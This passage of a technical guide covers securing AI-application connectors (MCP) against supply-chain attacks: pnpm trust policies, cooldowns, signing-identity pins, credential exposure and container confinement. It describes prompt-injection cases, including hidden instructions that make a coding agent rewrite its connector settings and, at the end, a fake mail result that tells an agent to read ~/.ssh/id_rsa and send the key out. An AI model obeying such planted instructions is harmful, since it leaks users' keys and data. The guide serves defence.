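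pnpm added the highest rank to fix false alarms about staged releases, but a package that stages one release and publishes the next directly now fails the check. npm has made staging the default for trusted publishing entries created since 3 September 2026, though projects can still allow direct publishing too. Those that use both methods will probably cause more of these failures.

### What the rule blocks, and what it catches

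To measure how often the rule blocks installs, Santos-Grueiro used pnpm 10.29.3 on 27 September 2026 to try installing the latest versions of the 1,000 most-downloaded npm packages and of 997 packages drawn at random from the most recently updated ones. The rule blocked 16 of the popular packages (1.6 percent) and 76 of the recently updated ones (7.6 percent). In a new sample of recently updated packages a week later, it blocked 9.2 percent. The recently updated packages are probably closer to a typical connector than the most-downloaded ones are. In most cases, the rule blocked a dependency rather than the package itself.

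A newer version of pnpm, 12.9.1, does somewhat better. If the newest suitable version of a dependency fails the check, pnpm looks for an older one that passes. With its default settings, pnpm 12.9.1 failed on 15 popular and 58 recently updated packages.

To assess the benefits, Santos-Grueiro reconstructed 12 attacks that used stolen credentials, from 2018 to the axios attack in 2026. They included 41 malicious releases of 15 packages on npm and PyPI. The registries had removed the releases, so Santos-Grueiro relied on advisories and post-mortems and, in a few cases, assumed that provenance was absent.

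| Measure | Malicious releases it would have stopped |
|---|---|
| No-downgrade rule | 17 of 41 |
| Strict one-day cooldown | 36 of 41 |
| Both together | 41 of 41 |
| Strict seven-day cooldown | 40 of 41 |

The rule stopped something in only 5 of the 12 attacks, because in the others, including the LiteLLM attack, the package had no earlier provenance or attestations to compare against. A larger count of npm malware advisories since April 2023 similarly found that only 17.5 percent of 1,654 attacked packages had provenance or a trusted publisher before the attack. That share is very uncertain (the study gives a range of 6.5 to 43.9 percent) because about half of the packages came from two large campaigns.

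Even the 17 successes depended on the attackers not trying to evade the rule. With the access they had, they could have got 15 of these releases past it. Thirteen followed earlier releases that had provenance but no trusted publisher. The attackers could have built those 13 packages in their own repository and obtained valid provenance, which pnpm would have ranked as highly as the earlier releases' provenance. The other two were the axios releases, where the attacker controlled the account and could have registered a different trusted publisher.

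This is a serious weakness when the rule is used alone, but it matters less for Ana because her Cosign command would still reject provenance from another repository.

### semver 6.3.1: a security fix that the rule blocks

Version 6.3.1 of `semver`, the library from the earlier Cosign example, caused 14 of the 16 failures among the popular packages. The library has about a billion downloads a week.

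In June 2023 the project fixed a flaw that let an attacker freeze a program with a specially written version number. It released the fix in version 7.5.2, with provenance. Many packages still used the older 6.x line, so in July a maintainer copied the fix to that line (a backport) and published version 6.3.1 by hand, without provenance.

pnpm orders releases by date and not by number. When it checks 6.3.1, it finds provenance on the earlier 7.5.2 and none on 6.3.1, and reports a "possible package takeover". There has been no later 6.x release, so every package that needs the 6.x line runs into the same error. A rule intended to make installations safer thus refuses the version that contains the security fix.

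A user asked pnpm to compare only releases with the same major version. This would allow 6.3.1 but also axios 0.30.4, because a thief with a stolen token can publish on any release line. pnpm's maintainers rejected the idea for that reason. In Santos-Grueiro's tests, keeping a separate history for each line removed up to 59 of the 92 failed installations but admitted 3 of the 17 malicious releases that the original rule had caught. The looser rule weakens protection on old release lines, which few people watch.

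pnpm offers an age limit instead. Kochan, in *pnpm 10.27*, describes a setting, `trustPolicyIgnoreAfter`, that skips the check for releases older than a chosen age. Every release that blocked a popular package was more than 600 days old, so even a limit of one year removed all 16 failures. A limit of 30 days still left 19 failures among the recently updated packages. The limit says nothing about whether an old release is safe. It relies on somebody having noticed by then if it wasn't.

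A harmless backport can look suspicious because of how it was published, as happened with the `uuid` library. On 29 April 2026, its maintainers backported a security fix to three older release lines. They published 13.0.1 by hand and the other two versions through the trusted publisher, and pnpm blocked only 13.0.1. Five days later they resolved the problem by releasing the fix again as 13.0.2 through the trusted publisher. Maintainers who want users to adopt strict rules can also publish their backports this way.

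### Why waiting a day catches so much

The malicious releases in the study stayed online for a median of 3.1 hours. Where the removal time is known, none lasted longer than two and a half days. Security companies scan new npm packages as they appear, so they can catch a malicious release before it has many victims. Likhith's company flagged the malicious Cline version 14 minutes after it was published.

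A three-day cooldown would therefore have excluded every release in the study with a known removal time. It would also have helped OpenAI. Adventures in Nodeland recounts that OpenAI's workflow for signing Mac applications had no minimum age for packages, and the malicious axios version reached it. OpenAI had to replace its signing certificates.

These attacks hit popular, widely watched packages. An obscure connector may get much less attention. Even a week's cooldown would not have kept out the malicious `postmark-mcp`, for example. Cooldowns are also weak against an author who is dishonest from the start, because there is no stolen account for anyone to notice.

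pnpm's *Mitigating supply chain attacks* describes a default cooldown of one day. Santos-Grueiro points out that this default is loose: if no old enough version fits, pnpm takes a newer one. Setting `minimumReleaseAge` explicitly makes it strict. The age limit for the trust check has to be longer than the cooldown, or the check will cover almost nothing. Of 588 public projects with both settings, 157 had got this wrong.

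### Pinning the signing identity without constant alarms

The no-downgrade rule detects when evidence disappears, but not when the signer changes. An identity pin covers that case by storing the signing identity of an earlier release and raising an alert if the next release's identity differs. The pin doesn't replace the rule, because it has nothing to compare when a release has no signature. None of the 41 malicious releases in the study would have triggered an identity pin.

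Because Ternmail's signing identity includes the tag, a pin on the full identity would raise an alert at every release. Santos-Grueiro tested several kinds of pin on 165 npm and PyPI packages with at least two signed releases:

| What the pin compares | Packages with at least one alert | A release from the branch `fix-timeouts` |
|---|---|---|
| The full identity, including the exact branch or tag | 75.8 percent | Alert |
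| The full identity, but with any tag accepted | 30.3 percent | Alert |
| The repository and workflow only | 13.9 percent | No alert |

A pin that leaves out the git ref raises the fewest alerts, but the ref is what exposed the Red Hat releases from short-lived branches. The study's compromise is to pin the repository and workflow file, accept any tag, and keep comparing branch names for projects that release from maintenance branches.

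The remaining alerts fall further if the pin remembers every branch it has accepted. In one sample, comparing each release only with the one before produced 232 alerts, and comparing it with the full list of earlier identities produced 26. If Ternmail releases from tags and also maintains an older version on a branch called `1.x`, Ana can put both in her Cosign pattern:

```
^https://github\.com/ternmail/connector/\.github/workflows/publish\.yml@refs/(tags/v[0-9.]+|heads/1\.x)$
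```

This accepts new version tags without editing and rejects `fix-timeouts`. It would also accept a tag that an attacker created, so the earlier test that the commit is on the main branch is still useful.

Pinning the npm account name gives little protection. In every case where Santos-Grueiro could identify the publisher, the attacker used an account that had published the package before. The axios attacker changed the account's e-mail address, so a pin that included the address would have caught both of the attacker's versions, but another attacker could easily leave it unchanged.

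### A policy for connectors

Ana or her company's security team can decide in advance how to respond to each result, because it is harder to be strict when a colleague is waiting for a connector to work.

| Result for the new version | What may have happened | Response |
|---|---|---|
| Valid attestation from the expected repository, workflow and ref | An ordinary release | Install it once it is three days old |
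| No attestation, and none on earlier releases | The project doesn't produce them | Confirm the name on the vendor's website, pin the digest, compare the package with the previous version, and record "none" as the expected value |
| No attestation, but earlier releases had one | A release by hand, or stolen credentials | Keep the old version unless someone grants an exception |
| Provenance, but no longer a trusted publisher or a staged release | A change in the release process, or a stolen token | Check the signing identity, then ask the vendor about the change |
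| Valid attestation from another repository | The project has moved, or an attacker built the package | Reject it until the vendor's own website confirms the move |
| Valid attestation from an unknown branch or workflow | A hurried fix, or an intruder in the repository | Reject it until the vendor explains |
| Invalid signature | An outdated verifier, or an altered file | Update the verifier and repeat the check. If it fails again, do not run the package |
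| No answer from the registry | Usually a network fault | Try again, and do not count it as "no attestation" |

Projects sometimes move their releases to a different repository. The Python libraries scikit-learn and matplotlib, for example, now sign their releases from separate release repositories. After such a move, the expected repository has to change.

An exception should cover one exact version. Suppose that one of Ternmail's dependencies needs `semver` 6.3.1. Before allowing it, Ana would take these steps:

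1. Look for an explanation from a source that an attacker would be unlikely to control. For `semver`, a public security advisory lists 6.3.1 as a fixed version. A comment on the project's GitHub page is weaker evidence. During the axios attack, the attacker used the maintainer's account to delete users' warnings, and another maintainer lacked the permissions to lock that account out.
2. Compare the release with the previous one on its line by running `npm diff --diff=semver@6.3.0 --diff=semver@6.3.1`. A backport should contain the fix and little else. The malicious axios versions would have shown a new dependency that nobody had announced.
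3. Write down the version, its digest, the reason and the date.
4. Remove the exception when the connector no longer needs that version.

Santos-Grueiro found 290 public projects that had exempted every version of at least one package. A user who exempted all of axios because of the harmless 0.30.3 would also have let in 0.30.4. *Trust policy downgrades*, from the documentation of aube, another package manager with a similar rule, recommends exempting only the affected version. But aube has a built-in exception list of 12 packages, including `eslint-config-prettier`, which attackers compromised in 2025. The list names packages without versions, which suggests that the exceptions cover every version. If they do, aube would not have flagged that attack.

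npx enforces none of this policy, so Ana has to apply it before the AI application starts the connector. She can do this by using pnpm for the installation. In a new folder, she creates a file called `pnpm-workspace.yaml`:

```yaml
trustPolicy: no-downgrade
trustPolicyExclude:
  - semver@6.3.1
minimumReleaseAge: 4320
```

The last number is three days in minutes. The exception has the form that Kochan, in *pnpm 10.22*, gives for exact versions. She then runs:

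```
pnpm add --save-exact @ternmail/connector@1.4.2
```

pnpm applies the rule and the cooldown to the connector and all its dependencies. It also stops if a dependency wants to run an install script that she hasn't allowed. If the installation succeeds and Cosign accepts the connector's provenance, she points the application's configuration at the file in this folder and starts it with `node`, as before. She shouldn't go back to a folder that npm installed, because npm may have chosen different versions of the dependencies.

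If a security fix can't wait three days, she can list that one version under `minimumReleaseAgeExclude`, after the same review as any other exception.

uvx has no equivalent of the no-downgrade rule. For a Python connector, Ana sets uv's `exclude-newer` option to three days, runs `pypi-attestations` on the new file with the expected repository, and looks up the previous release if the new one has no attestation. The configuration then uses `uv run --locked`, so that the application starts the versions she has checked. In a company, one person can do this work and give colleagues the finished lock file and settings, which is also the easiest way to keep them from pasting the original `npx -y` line back in.

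## Why an unsigned connector that starts processes carries more risk

Ana's policy lets her install a connector that has never had an attestation, after a few extra checks. The policy doesn't depend on what the connector could do once it runs, even though that determines how much a mistake would harm her.

### What a local process inherits

People use "spawns processes" in two senses when describing a connector. It can mean that the AI application starts the connector as a local process, which happens with every stdio connector, or that the connector itself starts other programs, such as a shell, `git` or a browser.

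*We Urgently Need Privilege Management in MCP* (Li, Li and colleagues, 2025) searched the source code of 2,562 connectors for sensitive operations. It found network operations in 1,438, file operations in 613 and system operations in 1,237, or 48 percent. System operations include changing settings as well as starting other programs, so the share of connectors that start programs may be lower. It may also be higher, because the search skipped third-party libraries, which may start programs too. These operations are not evidence of misuse, since a connector for `git`, for example, has to run `git`.

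| | Local connector | Program that the connector starts | Remote connector |
|---|---|---|---|
| Files | Everything that Ana's account can open | The same | Only what the application sends |
| Environment variables | A short default list and the `env` block of the configuration | Normally a copy of the connector's | None |
| Credentials | Keys in the `env` block and any in Ana's files | The same, and any login that the program has saved | The token that Ana grants it |
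| Network | Everything the laptop can reach, including office servers | The same | The operator's own network |

A connector can open `~/.ssh` and `~/.aws`, where many developers keep the keys to their servers and cloud accounts, whatever environment variables it receives. Chi raises the risk to files in *npx MCP server install is not installation*, and also warns that a connector started with npx gets the user's whole shell environment. However, applications that use the official Python library pass on only variables "deemed safe to inherit", according to Model Context Protocol.

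Starting a shell gives malicious code hardly any extra access, because the connector already has Ana's permissions. It adds more risk when the connector isn't malicious. If such a connector pastes text from the agent into a shell command, an attacker may be able to insert their own command through an email or web page the agent reads. Programs started by a connector can also keep running after the application closes the connector, and the connector's provenance doesn't cover them.

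A remote connector has none of this access. Ternmail's would receive Ana's searches and a token for her mailbox, but Ternmail already stores that mailbox. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* explains that a hostile operator can still attack the AI application. During login, the operator supplies web addresses for the application to open. One of them could point to a server inside the company's network, or contain text that a careless application passes to a shell. These attacks only work if the application has a flaw, which a malicious local connector doesn't need.

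### The keys in the configuration file

Many connectors need a password or key for the service they use. Trail of Bits' *Insecure credential storage plagues MCP* (2025) notes that MCP has supported OAuth, which issues short-lived, limited tokens, since March 2025. But some services don't support OAuth, so their users have to give the connector a long-lived key, often through a configuration file.

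*State of MCP Server Security 2025* (Skverer, 2025) used a language model to read the README files of about 5,200 connectors. About 53 percent relied on long-lived keys or access tokens, and 8.5 percent used OAuth. Connectors received 79 percent of the API keys through environment variables.

Skverer's estimate that 88 percent of connectors need credentials is less certain. It appears to include 26.4 percent for which the model couldn't identify the credential type, and Skverer admits the model probably misjudged some of them. The sample also favoured popular projects. Even so, long-lived keys were clearly much more common than OAuth in 2025.

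This configuration shows why one connector's keys are also at risk from the others. The second connector is fictional too:

```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "mail": {
      "command": "node",
      "args": ["/home/ana/ternmail/node_modules/@ternmail/connector/dist/index.js"],
      "env": { "TERNMAIL_TOKEN": "..." }
    },
    "invoices": {
      "command": "npx",
      "args": ["-y", "invoice-sorter-mcp"]
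    }
  }
}
```

The application gives `TERNMAIL_TOKEN` only to the mail connector, but the invoice connector runs under the same account, so it can read the token from the configuration file. The unsigned invoice connector could therefore expose Ana's mail even if she checked Ternmail's package correctly.

Skverer's employer, Astrix, offers a tool that fetches each key from a secure store when the connector starts. This keeps the key out of the file, but the connector still receives it.

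### OX Security and the question of who chooses the command

In April 2026, OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* described the stdio transport as a "critical, systemic vulnerability" at the core of MCP. The official libraries accept a command and its arguments, then start whatever program they specify. Cantina, another security company, reproduces the code from the Python and TypeScript versions, and neither excerpt checks that the program is a connector.

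This becomes dangerous when someone other than the user can influence the command. OX Security found four ways to do that:

- Some AI frameworks had web pages where outsiders could enter a connector's configuration.
- Some products restricted which commands were possible, but the researchers got around the restrictions.
- Hidden instructions could make a coding agent change its own connector settings. In the code editor Windsurf, this worked without any action by the user.
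- Nine of 11 connector marketplaces accepted a harmless test entry from the researchers.

The researchers ran commands on six live services and listed ten affected products, three of them marked as patched. Their figure of 150 million is for downloads, not vulnerable installations, and their figure of 200,000 exposed servers is an upper estimate. flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report* puts the number OX Security confirmed at 7,374.

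Anthropic declined to change the design. According to flyingpenguin, the company replied in January that "we believe that this design does represent a secure default". The developers of LangChain and FastMCP, two toolkits for AI applications, also considered the behaviour intentional. The protocol's maintainers agree in Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy*, which states that a malicious server "already has arbitrary code execution by virtue of being run". It adds that the stdio transport "is not a sandbox" and leaves isolation to whoever deploys the connector.

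ARMO, also a security company, objects to calling this a vulnerability. It points out that Jupyter, a popular tool for data analysis, has started programs from configuration files for about a decade. According to SecurityWeek, OX Security answers that the design leaves security entirely to the developers who build on MCP.

The maintainers are right that an application has to run some command to start a local connector. If Ana has chosen `node` and the path to Ternmail's file, she wants the application to run exactly that. But OX Security showed that many developers had let outsiders choose the command, and safer defaults could protect those developers' users. One of its proposals, a list of permitted commands, would help less than it seems. The researchers got past such a list in a product called Upsonic by using the arguments of npm and npx, and a list for connectors would almost have to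 allow both commands.

None of this depends on where a package came from:

| | An outsider chooses the command | An outsider controls the package |
|---|---|---|
| Example | A web page tricks Ana's coding agent into adding an entry that starts a shell | A thief publishes a malicious version of the connector that Ana chose |
| What a check of Ternmail's attestation shows | Nothing wrong, because the attack doesn't touch Ternmail's package | A missing attestation or an unexpected identity, unless the thief used the official workflow |
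| What helps | Approval of every change to the configuration | Pins, attestations and a cooldown |

The Model Context Protocol requires applications with one-click installation to show the complete command and ask for approval. Cantina recommends preventing agents from editing connector settings without approval. Ana can keep a copy of her configuration file and occasionally use `diff` to compare it with the current version.

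### Why blocking install scripts doesn't block the connector

A malicious package can run code at several moments, and npm 12's new default covers only the earliest.

| When code runs | What runs | Does npm 12 block it by default? | An attack that used it |
|---|---|---|---|
| During installation | Install scripts of the package and its dependencies | Yes | Cline 2.3.0 |
| When the application starts the connector | The main file and every library it loads | No | `dforge-mcp` |
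| When the agent uses a tool | The function behind that tool | No | `postmark-mcp` |

GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) explains that the block on install scripts also covers packages without an explicit script if they contain a `binding.gyp` file, which makes npm compile code. According to npm, the same default applies to npx.

A developer may not run an ordinary library until weeks after installing it, if ever, and that delay can make a real difference. With a connector, the attacker faces no such delay.

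The block can also stop a legitimate connector from working, for example if its database library has to compile a component. In the connector's folder, Ana can list the scripts that npm has not yet approved and allow one after reading it:

```
npm install-scripts ls
npm install-scripts approve some-database-library
```

By default, npm records the approval only for the installed version, so a later version needs a new one. npx has no project file for recording approvals. A user can instead save a general permission with `npm config set allow-scripts`, but it also applies to other npx commands.

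### How much a missing attestation raises the odds

A connector without an attestation is only slightly more likely to be malicious than one picked at random, because most legitimate packages also lack attestations. Bayes' theorem, the rule for updating a probability given new evidence, gives the size of the difference.

Suppose that 100 of every 100,000 releases are malicious and that 95 of those 100 have no attestation. These numbers are invented. Suppose also that 74 percent of legitimate releases have no attestation, which is the share of randomly chosen npm packages without provenance in Santos-Grueiro's study. The last column covers packages whose earlier releases all had attestations, and uses an invented figure of 1 percent for the share of their legitimate releases that lack one.

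| | Any package | Package that always had attestations |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious releases | 100 | 100 |
| Malicious releases without an attestation | 95 | 95 |
| Legitimate releases | 99,900 | 99,900 |
| Legitimate releases without an attestation | 73,926 | 999 |
| Chance that a release without an attestation is malicious | 95 in 74,021, or 0.13 percent | 95 in 1,094, or 8.7 percent |

For packages in general, a missing attestation raises the chance that a release is malicious from 1 in 1,000 to about 1 in 780. Even if every malicious release lacked an attestation, the chance would rise only to 1 in 740. For a package whose earlier releases all had attestations, a missing one raises the chance to about 1 in 12, so Ana's policy treats the two cases very differently.

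If 95 percent of legitimate connectors had no attestation, a missing attestation would not help identify malicious ones, because the same percentage of those would lack one. The percentage of malicious releases without attestations may also change. In Santos-Grueiro's census of 4,229 malicious npm versions, attackers published 119 through a project's own trusted publisher. From around January 2027, GitHub plans to stop access tokens that bypass two-factor authentication from publishing directly. Attackers who steal such tokens will then need a maintainer's approval or another way to publish. If more of them use official workflows, more malicious releases will have valid attestations.

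The damage a malicious connector could do is a better reason for caution. If the chance that the connector is malicious rises from 1 in 1,000 to 1 in 780, the expected loss rises by 28 percent. Giving the same connector Ana's whole account instead of an empty container could raise the expected loss a thousandfold, since she could lose her mail, her server keys and access to the company's network.

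Ana is also less likely to find the problem beforehand, because without provenance she has only the publisher's word that the package was built from the code in the repository.

An attack through an unsigned connector would also take longer to investigate. After the Ultralytics attack, investigators used attestations to narrow the search. Without them, investigators have to consider a stolen token, an infected laptop and a malicious maintainer, and may not know which earlier versions to suspect. Once npm has deleted the package, they also have no entry in Sigstore's log to consult.

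These reasons justify stricter limits on an unsigned connector, but a signed connector still needs tight limits, since the malicious `dforge-mcp` release had valid provenance. GitHub's *Defending against dependency supply chain attacks* (2025) advises only high-security environments to block packages that lack an attestation.

### Matching the access to the evidence

An unconfined connector that only works out public holidays can do as much harm as one that runs shell commands, because both have Ana's permissions. But the holiday connector doesn't need those permissions, so she can remove nearly all of them. This table's columns therefore describe the access that remains after confinement.

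| Evidence | Confined, no credentials | Confined, one narrow credential | Ana's whole account, or commands on her files |
|---|---|---|---|
| Expected attestation, and someone she trusts has reviewed the code | Run | Run | Run, and review each update |
| Expected attestation, but no review | Run | Run | Review the code first, or confine it |
| Never had an attestation | Run a pinned version | Run if the vendor confirms the package and Ana can revoke the credential | Do not run on her laptop |
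| Weaker evidence than before, or an unexpected signer | Keep the old version | Keep the old version | Keep the old version |

Version 1.4.2 of Ternmail's connector has the expected attestation. Suppose Ana hasn't read its code. It needs access to her mail but not her files, so it belongs in the middle column, and she can run it in a container with a limited mail token.

A fictional connector called `holiday-dates-mcp` has never had an attestation. It calculates public holidays from a built-in table, so a user can pin it and run it without credentials, file access or a network connection. If it is malicious, it can give the agent false dates and perhaps misleading instructions, but it can't open the user's mail.

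The third connector, `repo-fixer-mcp` (also fictional), is unsigned. It runs `git` and shell commands in a developer's projects and requests a GitHub token that can change every repository. Ana shouldn't run it on her laptop. If she needs it, she can run it in a virtual machine with a copy of one project and a token for that repository only, then review its changes before copying them back. A remote connector or one with an attestation may do the same job.

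### Running the connector in a container

Ana can put the connector that she has already installed and checked into a container. This configuration uses an official Node.js image and replaces the direct `node` command:

```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "mail": {
      "command": "docker",
      "args": [
        "run", "-i", "--rm", "--read-only",
        "--user", "1000:1000", "--cap-drop", "ALL",
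        "--security-opt", "no-new-privileges",
        "--network", "ternmail-only",
        "--mount", "type=bind,src=/home/ana/ternmail,dst=/app,readonly",
        "-e", "TERNMAIL_TOKEN",
        "node@sha256:77ac...",
        "node", "/app/node_modules/@ternmail/connector/dist/index.js"
      ],
      "env": { "TERNMAIL_TOKEN": "..." }
    }
  }
}
```

| Setting | Effect |
|---|---|
| `--mount` | The connector can read its own folder but nothing else in Ana's home folder |
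| `--read-only` | It can't change the files in the image |
| `--user`, `--cap-drop` and `no-new-privileges` | It runs without administrator rights and can't acquire them |
| `--network` | It can use only the network called `ternmail-only` |
| `-e` | It receives this one variable from the application |

If a dependency contains compiled code, Ana has to install the packages inside the same image, because a library compiled for macOS won't run in a Linux container.

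The command `docker network create --internal ternmail-only` creates a network with no route to the internet. Ana then adds a proxy, a small program that forwards connections, and sets it to allow only Ternmail's mail server. The connector has to support the proxy to reach the mail server. For `holiday-dates-mcp`, the setting `--network none` is enough.

Archestra's *MCP STDIO Command Injection* similarly recommends no home folder, no outbound connections by default and a limited environment. Ana should also never give a connector access to Docker's control socket, usually `/var/run/docker.sock`, because a program that can send Docker commands can start a new container that has access to all her files.

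A separate user account is simpler and keeps the connector out of Ana's files, as long as her home folder is closed to other accounts, but it doesn't restrict the connector's network access. A virtual machine takes more memory but protects the computer better when a connector has to run many other programs, because a container shares the core of the operating system with the rest of the computer. An attacker who finds a flaw in that core may be able to break out of the container.

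Ana should also limit the token. If Ternmail offers the choice, she should create a separate token for this connector, with permission to search mail and save drafts but not to send or delete anything. It should expire after a few weeks. She would then send each draft herself, which is less convenient but stops the connector from sending mail on its own.

### What confinement can't prevent

A confined connector can still misuse the access it needs for its job. A container that allowed connections only to Postmark would have let through every blind copy from `postmark-mcp`. Ternmail's connector could hide messages from the agent or invent them. If its token can send mail, it could also forward Ana's mail through Ternmail's own server.

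An attack can also leave the container through files. If Ana lets a coding connector write to a project folder, the connector can add a malicious script there. The script does nothing inside the container, but if she later runs the project on her laptop, the script will have her full permissions.

Confinement doesn't stop tool poisoning either, and hidden instructions can be in a tool's results as well as in its description. A malicious mail connector with no access to files might return a fake message that asks the agent to open `~/.ssh/id_rsa` with a file connector and put the contents into the next mail search. If the agent obeys, the mail connector receives the key as an ordinary search term. The container would not block any of these steps, so Ana should avoid using a connector she doesn't trust in the same session as connectors that can read private files or run commands.
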